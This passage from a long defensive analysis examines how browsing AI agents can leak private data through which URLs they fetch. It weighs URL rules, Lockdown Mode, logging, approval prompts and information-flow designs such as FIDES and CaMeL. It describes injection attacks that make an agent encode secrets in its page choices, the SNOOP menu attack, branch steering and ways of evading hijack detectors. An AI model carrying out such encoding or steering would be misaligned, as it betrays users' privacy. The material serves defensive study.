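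Claude's chat app has fallen between the two since the repair. It no longer counts links on the attacker's page as known, so the attacker would have to get prepared pages into Claude's search results or persuade the user to paste the URLs into the chat. Persuading the user may be easier than it sounds, because people often paste long emails and documents without checking every link. But all of these rules prevent the agent from putting a whole email into one request, which Superhuman's assistant did with a Google Form.

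### What the rules block that users want

The rules also differ in which legitimate requests they stop. In the table below, "unverified" means ChatGPT looks for another source or shows the user a warning. The entries follow from each rule's published description, except the one for pasted links in ChatGPT, which relies on Rehberger's understanding.

| What the agent needs to open | ChatGPT with the public index | Claude API, default settings | Claude chat since the repair |
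|---|---|---|---|
| A link the user pasted | opens | opens | opens |
| A well-known article linked from a fetched page | opens | opens | blocked unless search returns it |
| An article published minutes ago, linked from a fetched page | unverified until the crawler finds it | opens | blocked unless search returns it |
| A private download link in the user's email | unverified | opens if the developer's own tool read the email | blocked |
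| A shop search for terms the user has just given | unverified | blocked | blocked |
| A form that puts the user's entries in the URL | unverified | blocked | blocked |

New pages are mainly a problem for OpenAI's rule, since a crawler needs time to find them. Someone who asks about this morning's news may get an older source or a warning. Claude's chat app has more trouble with ordinary links. If a documentation page links to a newer version, Claude has to find that version through search or ask the user to paste the address.

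Every version of this policy has trouble with private links. A private download link should never appear in a public index, so ChatGPT will treat it as unverified even when the user wants the file. The Claude API's fetch tool may accept a private link from an email, but it rejects URLs longer than 250 characters, and many signed links exceed that. Its credential check may block others, because a signature can look like a key. If the user pastes the link into the chat, it passes the credential check, but the length limit still applies.

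Site searches and forms usually require the agent to compose a URL from something the user said, which these rules prevent. The agent can sometimes work around this. To check a price, it can use its search tool to find the shop's page for the product and open the result. It can track a parcel only if the carrier's email contains a complete tracking link and the rule accepts links from email.

An exact-URL rule offers little protection if the agent has a full browser and can fill in forms. Many forms send their contents in the body of a POST request to a URL that has been public for years, so the request would pass the check whatever the agent had typed. A tool that can send request bodies therefore needs a separate rule for them.

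This restriction does not always block the right requests. If an honest pharmacy's site has a search box but no ready-made link for metformin, Claude's API tool will refuse the search that Ana asked for. A dishonest pharmacy can put links to searches for a hundred medicines on its home page. The tool will then let Ben's agent open the one for metformin, because the URL came from a page it had already fetched.

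## How much can leak through the choice among permitted URLs?

OpenAI's index check keeps an agent from quietly putting private data into a URL. But the agent can still choose among indexed pages, and the owner of those pages can see in the server's log which ones it opened. A few such choices can encode a name or a diagnosis, though not a whole email.

### Counting the possible logs

Suppose an attacker has N permitted URLs and plants an instruction telling the agent which one to open for each possible value of a secret. After one fetch, the log can show any of N entries, so the attacker can distinguish at most N values, or log₂(N) bits. After k fetches in a known order, there are Nᵏ possible logs, so the limit is k·log₂(N) bits.

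With 36 URLs, one for each letter and digit, a fetch carries at most 5.17 bits. The limit for eight fetches depends on whether the agent may open a URL twice and whether the attacker can recover the order.

| Eight fetches from 36 URLs | Possible logs | Limit in bits |
|---|---|---|
| Order known, repeats possible | 36⁸, about 2.8 trillion | 41.36 |
| Order known, no repeats | 36!/28!, about 1.2 trillion | 40.15 |
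| Order lost, repeats possible | about 145 million | 27.11 |
| Order lost, no repeats | about 30 million | 24.85 |

About 33 bits are enough to single out one person among eight billion. A random 20-character key drawn from 64 symbols holds 120 bits, so leaking it at 5 bits per fetch would take 24 fetches. A 2,000-character email, spelled out one character per fetch, would take 2,000 fetches. *The Read-Only Lie*, a 2026 blog post, applies the same formula to the Memory Heist. The site used there offered 27 links per page, or 4.75 bits per fetch, so about 30 fetches could leak at most roughly 143 bits.

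Spelling out a secret one letter at a time uses more fetches than necessary. Embrace The Red points out that an attacker could use thousands of indexed URLs and teach the model a larger vocabulary. With 1,000 URLs, each fetch carries almost 10 bits. If each URL stands for one common medicine, a single fetch reveals what Ben takes, while spelling "metformin" takes nine fetches.

Some secrets can be leaked in a single bit. An injected instruction could tell the agent to open a certain page if the user's mail mentions a merger, and otherwise to do nothing. *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* acknowledges that an agent can always leak one bit by either sending a message or not. The harm depends on which question the attacker uses that bit to answer.

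### How well do real agents transmit?

These figures are upper limits, and an agent that opens the wrong page transmits less. Liang, Deng and colleagues (2026) measured these errors in *Actions Speak Louder than Words*. Their page offered an agent four references on different subjects, only one of which matched what the agent was looking for. They then tried to infer the matching reference from the requests their server received.

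When each reference had its own URL, the choice of URL identified the right reference in 93.8% of the trials that produced a signal, compared with 25% for guessing. If the errors fall evenly on the other three references, each choice carries about 1.57 of a possible 2 bits. The order and timing of requests were less reliable signals, giving the right answer 67.9% and 58.6% of the time, respectively.

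In their full attack, SNOOP, the attacker places a link on a page the agent is likely to read. The link leads to a site with a menu of references, and the attacker never asks the agent to send private data. In their example, a user asks why influenza can be more severe than COVID-19 in children. The agent opens `/ref/B` for biological mechanisms and then `/ref/B1` for immune response, so the site's owner learns what the agent is researching.

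On 500 questions from StackExchange, a network of question-and-answer sites, SNOOP needed 6.5 probes per question on average. It recovered the concepts in the questions with an F1 score of 0.89, where 1 means it found every concept and added no wrong ones. Four published agent defences changed its scores by less than 0.03.

None of those four was an exact-URL rule. OpenAI's index would block menu pages with newly invented addresses. But an attacker could get a set of addresses like `/ref/B` indexed and later change the text behind them, since the addresses don't describe their content. The agent opens these pages because they look useful for the user's task, so a check on whether each fetch serves that task would let them through too.

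### The confinement problem

*A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) asks how a customer can run someone else's program on confidential data without the data leaking to the program's owner. One possible leak is through the customer's bill, because the owner must receive a copy and a dishonest program can encode data in it. Restricting the bill's format reduces the leak to a few bits or tens of bits, but eliminating it requires "more far-reaching measures".

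Lampson called the bill a legitimate channel. He reserved the term "covert channel" for things not meant to carry information at all, such as a program's effect on the load of a shared computer. Later writers use the term more broadly, and now commonly include the choice of which page to open. Under Lampson's definitions, a page request is closer to the bill, because the server has to receive it.

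Lampson considered forbidding the program to call any other program but found this impractical. His more workable principle was masking, under which the customer determines everything the program puts into these channels. For a browsing agent, this would mean fixing the list of requests without reference to the private data. For cases where masking is too burdensome and the customer can accept some leakage, he suggested limiting the channels' capacity.

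### Measuring what web traffic could carry

Borders and Prakash applied the idea of a limit to web browsing in a 2008 workshop paper, *Towards Quantification of Network-Based Information Leaks via HTTP*. They considered it impossible in general to detect disguised sensitive data, so they measured the most information a request could contain. They returned to the subject in *Quantifying Information Leaks in Outbound Web Traffic* (2009). Borders's 2009 patent application, *Method, system and computer program product for comparing or measuring information content*, sets out a fuller method with results.

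The monitor reads both outgoing requests and the pages servers send back. It collects the links on each page, running the page's scripts to find more, and sorts them into groups, such as images the browser loads automatically and links a person has to click. When a request matches a link, the monitor counts 2 bits for the group and log₂(n) bits for the choice among the n links in that group. A click on one of 64 links therefore counts as 8 bits, however long the URL is.

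If a requested URL differs from every known link, the monitor adds to its count the size of the changes needed to turn the closest link into that URL. Adding a secret to a URL raises the count however the secret is encoded. The monitor also counts timing, at 6 bits for a request made within three seconds of the previous one.

Borders tested this on 507,505 requests that ten people made over 30 days. The average request was 980 bytes long, but the monitor counted only 15.8 bytes as information that could have come from the user's computer. In a separate test on a blog with almost no dynamic links, the average was 1.9 bytes. Link choice there accounted for 86 bytes over 136 requests, or about 5 bits each, which is close to the figure for 36 URLs.

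The method makes bulk theft easy to spot. A 100-kilobyte leak blended into a day's raw traffic but stood out clearly once the monitor subtracted the predictable part. The eight-fetch leak in the table, however, is only about 5 bytes, less than the monitor counts for one average request.

### Why the subtraction is harder for an agent

A person mostly clicks links on the page in front of them, so n is often small. An agent under a public-index rule can go to any indexed page it remembers or finds through search. If the index held a billion URLs, the monitor would have to count about 30 bits for each fetch, even in a session with no leak. This is a valid upper bound, but it is too high to help an operator spot a leak of 5 or 10 bits.

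For human browsing, Borders suggests a way to lower the count when the organisation trusts the user and worries only about malicious software. A trusted device can record mouse and keyboard input, and the monitor can subtract whatever follows from it. With an agent, the click comes from the model, which a planted instruction may have influenced. The user's typed request is trustworthy, but a request such as "find out why my washing machine shows this error" does not determine which pages the model will open.

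The operator could try to predict the model's choices by running it a second time without the private data. TightLip, an earlier system that Borders describes, did this with ordinary programs. It ran a shadow copy of the program without access to the sensitive files, and marked any output that differed between the two copies as confidential. But two runs of a language model can choose different pages even on identical input, so the private data may not be the cause of a difference. The task may also depend on the private data, as when a user asks the agent to research the illness named in a doctor's letter.

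### What each limit removes

The limit, k·log₂(N), grows in proportion to the number of fetches (k) but only logarithmically with the number of URLs (N). Halving the number of URLs the attacker can choose from therefore lowers the limit by one bit per fetch, while halving the number of fetches halves it. A cap of three fetches per site reduces the limit for 36 URLs from 41.36 bits to 15.5. Even with 1,000 URLs, three fetches carry at most 30 bits.

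Such a cap also stops an agent from reading a manual spread over twenty pages or comparing a dozen products in one shop. An attacker with several domains gets a new allowance on each, so the operator would also need a limit for the whole session, which hurts long research tasks. That limit would also reset with each new session.

Caching and bans on repeat visits do much less. With either measure, the site logs each URL at most once, which lowers the limit for eight fetches from 41.36 to 40.15 bits. With 1,000 URLs, the reduction is only about 0.04 bits out of nearly 80. These measures matter more when the attacker has only a few pages, because the agent soon runs out of new ones to open. They also interfere with tasks that require repeated checks, such as watching for concert tickets or tracking a parcel. A cache that lasts a few minutes, as Embrace The Red proposes, interferes less than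 a ban.

In theory, reordering removes more. If the proxy holds eight different requests and sends them in random order, the limit falls from 40.15 to 24.85 bits. But an attacker could restore the full 41.36 bits with numbered URLs like those in ZombieAgent, using 288 URLs for eight positions. The proxy also cannot hold back a request if the agent needs the answer to choose the next page, so reordering suits fetching a batch of search results better than following links through a website.

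Random delay reduces the information leaked through request timing, which is in addition to the k·log₂(N) bits leaked through the choice of URLs. Borders estimates that a random delay of up to one second would remove 5 bits of timing information per request, though widening the timing interval from 0.06 seconds to one second accounts for only about 4. *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* notes that random delays only reduce a timing channel, and that closing it requires sending requests at a constant pace. Both measures slow every page the agent opens without hiding which pages it opened.

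Liang and colleagues tested a remedy similar to Lampson's masking. Their Selection-Obfuscated Retrieval downloads pages under a fixed budget independent of the private context, and the agent then chooses among the local copies. SNOOP's score on the StackExchange questions fell from 0.89 to 0.39, so the attacker still recovered some information. The extra downloads use bandwidth, and the page the agent needs may fall outside the budget.

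### Reading from stored copies

An agent can also read stored copies of pages, as Codex's web search does by default. If a crawler saved those copies before the session began, the agent's choice of pages adds nothing to the attacker's log. Even if Ben's agent followed the planted instruction and opened the page for metformin, the pharmacy would not find out.

This holds only if the store never contacts a site because of what an agent requested. If it downloads a missing page on demand, or refreshes an old copy when an agent opens it, the site's owner receives the same signal as before. The store has to refuse requests for pages it lacks and update the pages it has on a schedule independent of any user's session.

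ChatGPT's optional Lockdown Mode works this way. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) states that it limits web browsing to cached content, "so no live network requests leave OpenAI's controlled network". OpenAI introduced the mode for organisations in February 2026, describing it as a tool for executives and security teams that most users do not need. In June, OpenAI began offering it to personal accounts. Willison (2026) responded that it "looks really good to me".

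Lockdown Mode disables or limits many of ChatGPT's features. According to OpenAI's help page, *Lockdown Mode*, search results may be stale or missing. A question about this morning's news or the current price of a flight may therefore get an old answer or none. Deep Research and Agent Mode, which browse on the user's behalf, do not work. ChatGPT cannot download files for analysis or retrieve images from the web, and users cannot let code written in its Canvas editor access the network.

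Lockdown Mode also leaves other routes open. It does not change network access in Codex. In managed workspaces, administrators decide which connected apps remain available, and OpenAI advises against enabling write actions whose results an attacker could see. A planted instruction in a cached page can still distort the answer. OpenAI does not guarantee that the setting prevents every leak. Users who need a live page can switch Lockdown Mode off for a single chat, which then loses the protection.

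## Can logs or user approval settle the doubtful cases?

Some requests are neither clearly safe nor clearly dangerous under any of the rules above. The site may be unknown but ordinary, or the URL may be public but a strange choice for the task. An operator can allow such a request and log it, or hold it and ask the user. Reviewers can often tell afterwards from a detailed log whether a planted instruction caused the fetch, and a user who sees the right information can sometimes tell immediately. But both methods take people's time, and injected fetches are probably so rare that most of that time would go to false alarms.

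A request leaks nothing if a policy blocks it or the user refuses it, but by the time a request appears in a log, the attacker's server already has the data. A company that finds a stolen API key in its log can still cancel the key, but it can't undo the disclosure if a pharmacy has learned that Ben takes metformin.

### What a log adds

A rule that judges each request separately cannot detect a secret split into four pieces, or a name spelled out by opening `/b`, `/e` and `/n`. A log lets the operator compare these requests. Monitoring software that compares them during the session can stop the agent before it sends the last pieces.

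Logs also record fetches that the agent's answer leaves out, as happened in 95% of the successful attacks in *Silent Egress*. After a leak, the company can use the logs to work out which keys it has to replace and which customers it has to tell.

Some leaks become clear only across many sessions. *AgentTell* (2026), a study of what browser agents reveal through their choices, distinguishes a leak, which happens in one session, from a channel, which is a pattern across sessions. An agent that opens the page for metformin might have opened it whatever its user's mail contained. To find out, an investigator would have to compare sessions of users with different private data.

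### What the record has to contain

An investigator who wants to know why a fetch happened needs more than the request.

| Item in the record | What it shows | Where software can record it |
|---|---|---|
| Full URL | Data in the path or query | Decrypting proxy or tool interface |
| Every redirect | Which servers received a request | Decrypting proxy, or a tool that handles each redirect itself |
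| Page content returned | Whether the page contained instructions | Decrypting proxy or tool interface |
| Tool call | Which session made the request, and what the model wrote | Tool interface |
| Everything the model had read before the call | Where the instruction and the data could have come from | The software that runs the agent |

A network log lacks the last two items. A decrypting proxy may have copies of the web pages the agent fetched, but not the user's request or the local files the model read. Its records also don't show which of those pages were in the model's context when it chose the next URL.

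Without decryption, an ordinary network log may not identify the agent. *Detecting Shadow AI* (Canale and Soulis, 2026), a study of how companies can find agents that employees run without approval, notes that network monitoring shows an encrypted connection but not the program that opened it. The paper's detector runs on the employee's computer and uses the computer's record of recent DNS lookups to match connections to AI providers. If the provider shares a content delivery network with other services, this works for only one to five minutes, until the record expires.

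Agents that run in the cloud leave no trace on the laptop. When the provider's servers fetch the page, as in ShadowLeak, the request never crosses the employer's network, so the employer has to rely on whatever records the provider keeps and shares.

The record must include the page as the agent received it, because an investigator who opens the URL later may get a different one. *A Whole New World* (2025) describes a site that identifies AI agents by their technical characteristics and shows planted instructions only to them. The site used in the Memory Heist also hid its pages from people. Telling visitors apart appears feasible, since the classifier in *Whose Agent Are You?* (2026) separated agents, crawlers and humans with 100% accuracy in a test with six agent frameworks.

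Existing logs often don't meet this standard. According to *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026), even detailed logging displays typically shorten URLs or summarise what a tool returned. A shortened URL may omit the part that carried the data.

A complete log can leak the credentials it records, and *Understanding and Evaluating Claw-like Agent Security Through a Computer-Systems Lens* (2026) lists unredacted tool-call logs among the places where this happens. An operator can replace known keys with fingerprints before saving the log and still see which key was sent out. The log should also be stored where the agent cannot read or change it. Help Net Security's *Your AI agent's system prompt is not a security control* reports that guidance from the SANS Institute, a security training organisation, and AWS, Amazon's cloud division, recommends sending every prompt, tool call and response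 to storage that nobody can alter.

### Ten attacks in a million fetches

Nobody can read a million log entries, so a detector has to select which ones a person sees. Like the secret scanners discussed earlier, it will raise mostly false alarms if attacks are rare. Suppose a hypothetical company's agents make 1,000,000 fetches in a month, of which 10 are injected, and the detector flags 99% of injected fetches and 1% of legitimate ones. It would raise about 10 true alerts and 10,000 false ones, so roughly one alert in a thousand would be real.

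The general formula for the share of alerts that are real, known as precision, is

precision = π·D / (π·D + (1 − π)·F)

where π is the share of fetches that are injected, D is the detection rate and F is the false-alarm rate. When π is tiny, F has far more influence than D. Perfect detection would add a tenth of an alert to the example. To make half the alerts real, the company would have to cut the false-alarm rate from 1% to about 0.001%.

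Stefan Axelsson made this argument about intrusion detection in 2000. The 2026 survey *AI-Driven Security Alert Screening and Alert Fatigue Mitigation in Security Operations Centers* still identifies the problem he described as a main cause of alert fatigue. It cites one large organisation where only about one in 10,000 daily alerts was linked to a real attack.

A company can improve the ratio by sending fewer legitimate fetches to the detector. If an exact-URL rule clears 95% of legitimate fetches beforehand, the 1% false-alarm rate produces about 500 false alerts instead of 10,000. However, the detector then no longer examines leaks that encode data in the choice of which public URLs to fetch.

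Requiring two independent checks to flag a fetch before raising an alert can also help. If each check has the rates above, false alerts fall to about 100, while on average 9.8 of the 10 attacks still raise an alert. But two checks that both flag long random strings are not independent, and signed download links would set off both.

Judging whole sessions helps only if the detector evaluates all the fetches together, rather than flagging any session that contains an alert. With a 1% false-alarm rate per fetch, a session of 50 legitimate fetches has a 39% chance of at least one false alarm, so reviewers would have to read more than a third of such sessions.

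A team can also read the most suspicious alerts first. *Can Risk-Based Alerting Mitigate Cybersecurity Alert Fatigue?* (Henze, 2026) tested ways of ranking alerts by risk on eight collections of security alerts. The best combinations reached an average AUROC of 0.92, versus 0.72 for sorting by severity label. Better ranking lets a small team use its time well, but the team still won't read the alert for an attack that ranks far down the list.

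### Detectors that read the agent's actions

Researchers have tested detectors on records of agents' tool calls, which contain more evidence than network traffic. *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents* (Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki, 2026) examined eleven such evaluations and found that attacks or anomalies made up 16% to 86% of the test samples. None varied that share to see how detectors perform when attacks are rare.

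In one set of tests, a detector that used the agent's choice of tools and features such as session length had a respectable AUROC of 0.879. It caught 77% of hijacked sessions and wrongly flagged 19% of the others. If 2% of sessions are hijacked, it would raise 12 false alerts for every true one. Precision also depended on the mix of harmless sessions, falling from 11.7% with ordinary sessions to 3.9% with sessions chosen to be hard to tell from attacks.

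These detectors also learned patterns specific to the benchmark they were built on. None of the detectors trained on AgentDrift did better than chance on another benchmark, AgentDojo. Some relied partly on the length of the text that tools returned, which an attacker controls. When 1,200 characters were added to the planted text, the detector described above caught 3% of attacks, down from 77%.

AlignmentCheck, a monitor released by Meta, held up better on the new benchmark. It gives a language model the user's request and the agent's actions, and asks whether the latest action pursues a goal the user did not set. It does not read the web pages, so text planted there cannot reach it directly. Running on Claude Sonnet 5.5, it flagged 88% of hijacked AgentDojo sessions and 3.8% of harmless ones. At a 2% attack rate, about a third of its alerts would be real. On AgentDrift, that share was only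 5%.

This is the best evidence here that a monitor can find hijacked sessions, but the monitor needs to see the user's request, which a network log does not contain. The tests covered tool calls in general and did not measure URL leaks separately. Abbasi and colleagues scored each session after it had finished, so even a correct alert came after the harm.

*Structural Baselines Matter for Agent Failure Detection and Attribution* (2026) reports the same effect for ordinary agent failures. Precision was 0.97 to 0.99 in a test where 87% of runs had failed. If only 1% of runs failed and the threshold wrongly flagged 10% of good runs, the same detector would have a precision of 0.06.

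### Learning what is normal

A behavioural baseline describes what an agent usually does, so that software can compare it with what the agent is doing now. SANS and AWS say in their guidance that models built for human users do not suit agents, since those models classify a coding agent that starts many processes at once as abnormal. Help Net Security reports that SANS and AWS advise monitoring the riskiest agents first and collecting at least 30 days of data before tuning any detection rules. It also points out that those agents are already running while the data is collected.

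AWS's *Agentic security* recommends "living baselines" that adapt as agents change. This avoids a flood of alerts after every update, but if an attacker changes an agent's behaviour slowly, the changes could become part of the baseline. Injected fetches during the first 30 days could also count as normal.

Baselines have worked well in tests on agents with fixed routines. *TraceAegis* (Liu, Ruan et al., 2025) learned the usual order of tool calls for two simulated agents, one that directs patients to hospital departments and one that files purchase requests. It used gateway logs of tool calls because defenders often cannot obtain an agent's prompts or reasoning. With DeepSeek-V3 checking the rules, its precision and recall were both about 0.96 on the hospital agent and 0.93 on the purchasing agent. In a company's internal attack exercise, it found 132 of 140 abnormal sequences.

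Abbasi and colleagues report that about half of the traces in the test set were abnormal. The hospital results imply a false-alarm rate of around 3%, so if one session in 1,000 were hijacked, only about 3% of the alerts would be real. A research agent would be harder to describe than either of these agents because it normally opens unfamiliar sites in a new order.

### What users do with approval prompts

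Asking users for approval before the fetch could separate two requests that look identical to a firewall. Unlike any detector, Ana and Ben know whether they asked for the price of metformin, and only Ana did.

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users of its coding agent approve 97% of permission prompts. This alone does not prove that users are careless, since most of the commands are probably safe. But users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, which suggests that they can be critical when a question seems worth reading.

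Anthropic also ran an experiment with 1,053 paid testers. Partway through a coding session, the researchers replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. Testers blocked about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session, but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts. An automated check blocked 89% of the same commands.

The vendor produced these figures and published them to justify replacing prompts with that automated check. The post does not report how often the check blocks harmless commands. The testers worked in a test environment with nothing of their own at risk. They also judged commands rather than URLs, though an encoded URL is probably no easier to judge than a plainly dangerous command.

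Anthropic calls the effect approval fatigue in *How we built Claude Code auto mode*. It is likely for fetches too, because injected ones are rare. Suppose an agent makes 100 fetches a day, one in 100,000 is injected, and the policy asks the user about 1% of legitimate fetches. The user then answers about one prompt a day and sees about 1,000 harmless ones before the first real attack. OpenAI gives a similar reason for avoiding strict site lists: frequent false alarms can train people to click through.

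Letting users write rules in advance does not necessarily help. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, had 113 people without software backgrounds supervise a simulated agent that sometimes exceeded its task. One group set standing rules of "allow", "ask" or "never" for actions such as spending money or sending information. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, so they still had to make most decisions when the agent was about to act. With these rules in place, the agent carried out 148 actions it should not have, and the users had approved 133 of them.

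That group saw an average of 10.9 prompts, compared with 18 for people who approved every action, but its rate of blocking overreach was 20 percentage points lower. So reducing the number of prompts does not by itself make people read them more carefully.

### When a prompt is informative

Many approval prompts leave out information the user needs to decide. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* points out that a user who approves a "web search" tool allows all its later requests without seeing their URLs. Some products show no prompt at all. In *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) examined five commercial agents and found no way to set permissions for the remote browser in ChatGPT's agent mode.

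Showing the user the URL before the agent opens it helps if the private data is readable. A user may notice their own email address after `?data=`, but not the same address in Base64, which looks no stranger than a legitimate signed download link. If the agent spells out a name by opening one page per letter, each approval prompt shows a harmless public URL. Even with OpenAI's link warning, the user has to work out what information the URL contains.

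*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) found the same problem with file access, where prompts show a command but not its effect. Approving `python3 setup.py` looks routine but permits whatever code the script contains. Problems with user review contributed to 105 of the 290 reports it examined. In 80 of those 105, the actions went through on automatic approval, and in 31 the prompt was uninformative.

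NVIDIA would ask users only about requests outside a tight allowlist, and would require a new approval each time, because permission for one connection should not cover later ones. Refusals need similar care. In *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, one interviewee refused several requests, then watched the agent try another approach and was unsure whether it still respected the limit. If a user refuses a suspicious fetch, the software could block the whole site for the rest of the session.

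For Ben, a useful prompt would say that the agent wants to send `shop.example` the word "metformin" from his doctor's email, although he asked only about delivery. He could answer that without knowing anything about URLs. But the software can write such a prompt only if it has tracked where the word came from.

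## What changes if the policy knows where the instruction and the data came from?

The program that runs an agent already handles evidence that a firewall lacks, including the user's request and every page and email the model reads. It could record that the word "metformin" came from a doctor's email and that the suggestion to search for it came from a pharmacy's home page. Anthropic's `url_sources` setting already uses one piece of this evidence, the source of the URL. Research systems also track the private data.

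### Labelling data as it arrives

Taint tracking labels each piece of data when it enters the agent and copies the label to anything derived from it. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a system built at Microsoft that uses two kinds of label. An integrity label marks data as trusted or untrusted, and a confidentiality label lists who may read it. The user's request is normally trusted and public. A web page is untrusted and public, while only the sender and recipients may read an email.

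Data made from several sources gets the strictest combination of their labels. It is untrusted if any source was untrusted, and only people who may read every source may read the result. If Alice, Bob and Carol may read one document, and Bob, Carol and Dan may read another, only Bob and Carol may read a summary of both.

The software checks the labels before each tool call. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026), a call that sends data out may go ahead if only trusted data influenced the decision to make the call, or if every recipient is allowed to read the data. The table applies this rule to an ordinary agent that requests the metformin search after reading the pharmacy's home page.

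| Session | Only trusted influence? | May the pharmacy read everything the agent has read? | Search |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ana asks for the price of metformin | no | yes | allowed |
| Ben asks about delivery, and the page sends his agent to his email | no | no | blocked |
| Ana asks for the price of the medicine in her doctor's email | no | no | blocked |

The rule distinguishes the first two sessions even though their URLs are identical. Ana's agent has read an untrusted page but nothing private, so it can leak only her request. Ben's agent has read his mail, which the pharmacy has no right to see.

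### Why cautious labels block too much

The rule makes a mistake in the third session, because Ana did ask for that search. Her agent has read the same kinds of data as Ben's, and the software cannot determine which data led the model to its decision. A language model processes everything in its context together, so FIDES treats each output as possibly dependent on all of it. Once an ordinary agent has read one web page and one private email, every later fetch from an outside site looks suspect.

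Costa and colleagues tested label checks on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks. Adding the checks to an ordinary GPT-4o agent cut the average share of tasks it completed from 84% to 42%, with no attack present. They mention one way to loosen the labels: estimate which messages influenced a response, then regenerate it from those messages alone. The response then needs only those messages' labels.

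Another approach is to ask the user about doubtful transfers. *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) starts from a rule that stops scripts on one website from reading another site's data. An agent gets around this rule because it remembers what it read on one site and can write it into another. The paper's defence, SOPGuard, labels data with the site it came from and carries the label into the agent's output. SOPGuard asks the user before the agent writes that output into a page on a different site.

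Ben could learn from such a question that data from his mail is about to go to `shop.example`. Wang and colleagues added SOPGuard to BrowserOS, an open-source browser with a built-in agent. In their tests, SOPGuard eliminated unauthorised transfers and increased running time by 2.07% to 5.79%. But a label that names only the site cannot stop a leak within that site, such as an agent copying a user's private messages on a forum into a public comment there.

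### Planning before reading

The confusion is easier to avoid if the part of the agent that chooses actions never reads the untrusted text. Rahman and Kim's split agent, described earlier, used this idea to stop leaks. Willison had proposed a general version in 2023, the dual-LLM pattern, in which one model plans and a second model with no tools reads the untrusted text.

CaMeL, a 2025 design from Google DeepMind, develops the pattern into a full system. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) describes how it works. The planning model receives the user's request and writes a complete program before any tool returns data. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, then runs the program. When a step needs information from a page or email, the interpreter gives the text to the reading model and stores its answer in a variable. Later steps can use the variable,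 but the planning model never receives its contents. The interpreter also limits what each step may do with the data.

For Ben's question about delivery, the planner would write a program that opens the pharmacy's page, has the reading model find the delivery charge, and reports it. No step opens his mail. The planted instruction reaches only the reading model, which has no tools and cannot add a step to the program. The instruction could still make that model report a false charge.

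When Ana asks about the medicine in her doctor's email, the program includes a step that reads the email and another that searches the pharmacy. Both steps come from her request, so the policy has evidence that Ana caused the search, which it lacked in the third row of the table.

FIDES uses the same separation but calls its planner again after every step. It hides a tool's result in a variable only if showing the result would tighten the labels on the planner's context. The planner can query the reading model about the hidden text or open the variable, which tightens the labels. Costa and colleagues suggest that a policy for sending messages require a trusted recipient but allow untrusted text. The equivalent rule for Ana's search would require the site to come from her request but let the search term come from the email.

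A web page could still trick the reading model into returning more than a medicine's name. FIDES can restrict the model's answer to a yes or no, or to a choice from a fixed list, and record that restriction in the label. A policy might then accept a yes-or-no answer from an untrusted page, because the page can influence the plan by only one bit.

The AgentDojo results show both the protection and the loss in task completion. All three agents used GPT-4o. The first column of figures counts successful attacks after the researchers removed cases that the benchmark had scored wrongly, and the other columns give the share of tasks completed with no attack present.

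| Agent | Successful attacks | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no checks | 152 | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent with label checks | 0 | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES with label checks | 0 | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

FIDES recovered some of the performance lost to the cautious labels, except on travel tasks, where the model often mishandled the variables. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES's completion rate on travel tasks rose from 41% to 68%. Kolluri and colleagues put the performance loss for designs of this kind, including CaMeL, at up to 30% on AgentDojo.

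They also argue that this comparison is unfair to the secure designs. The undefended agent completes its tasks only because nobody has to approve its actions, whereas many real products ask before any action with consequences. If an ordinary agent running on o3-mini had to stop for approval before each of these actions, it would finish 24.3% of the tasks without help. FIDES finished 50.1%, and PRUDENTIA, a version of FIDES whose planner is told the policy and takes it into account, finished 59.1%.

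PRUDENTIA can also ask the user to vouch for a piece of text instead of approving each action that follows from it. If an email lists ten chores, the user answers one question instead of ten. The security results assume that the user would spot an attack and refuse, which few of the testers in Anthropic's experiment did. One careless approval of an email with hidden instructions would also allow every action in those instructions.

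Even without that mistake, an agent using FIDES can still leak a little private information through its choice of page. FIDES enforces what Costa and colleagues call explicit secrecy, which covers private data copied into a tool call but not what an observer can infer from which calls the agent makes. Preventing such leaks would essentially mean forbidding every publicly visible call after the agent had read anything private.

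### Why web pages are the hard case

A planner that never sees a page can still handle tasks whose steps are known in advance, such as sending a summary of three emails to a colleague. Costa and colleagues call such tasks data-independent. Web research is mostly data-dependent, because the pages often supply the next address to open.

The planner can prepare for this by writing a branch for each situation it expects. Foerster and colleagues tried this with agents that operate a computer through its screen. Their programs averaged 41.1 tool calls and 39.7 branches, compared with 4.9 calls and 3.7 branches for CaMeL programs for AgentDojo. About half of each program consisted of fallbacks that a given run never used.

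They report that their system kept up to 57% of a frontier model's performance on OSWorld, a benchmark of everyday computer tasks, when allowed five attempts per task. Without the separation, Claude Sonnet 4.5 solved 109 of the automatically scored tasks. With the separate planner, the system solved 62 of those within five attempts, but only 31 (28%) on the first. It used 1.88 times as many tokens as the undefended agent. The FIDES version used 29.6 times as many because it sends the whole history to the planner at every step.

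An attacker can also influence which branch of the plan the agent follows. Many plans include a step to find and dismiss a cookie notice. The researchers put a fake notice inside an advertisement, and the reading model sent the agent to click on it, which opened the attacker's site. The page had given no instruction and added no step to the plan. The researchers call this branch steering. It resembles the implicit attacks that capabilities cannot prevent, as Rajani and colleagues proved.

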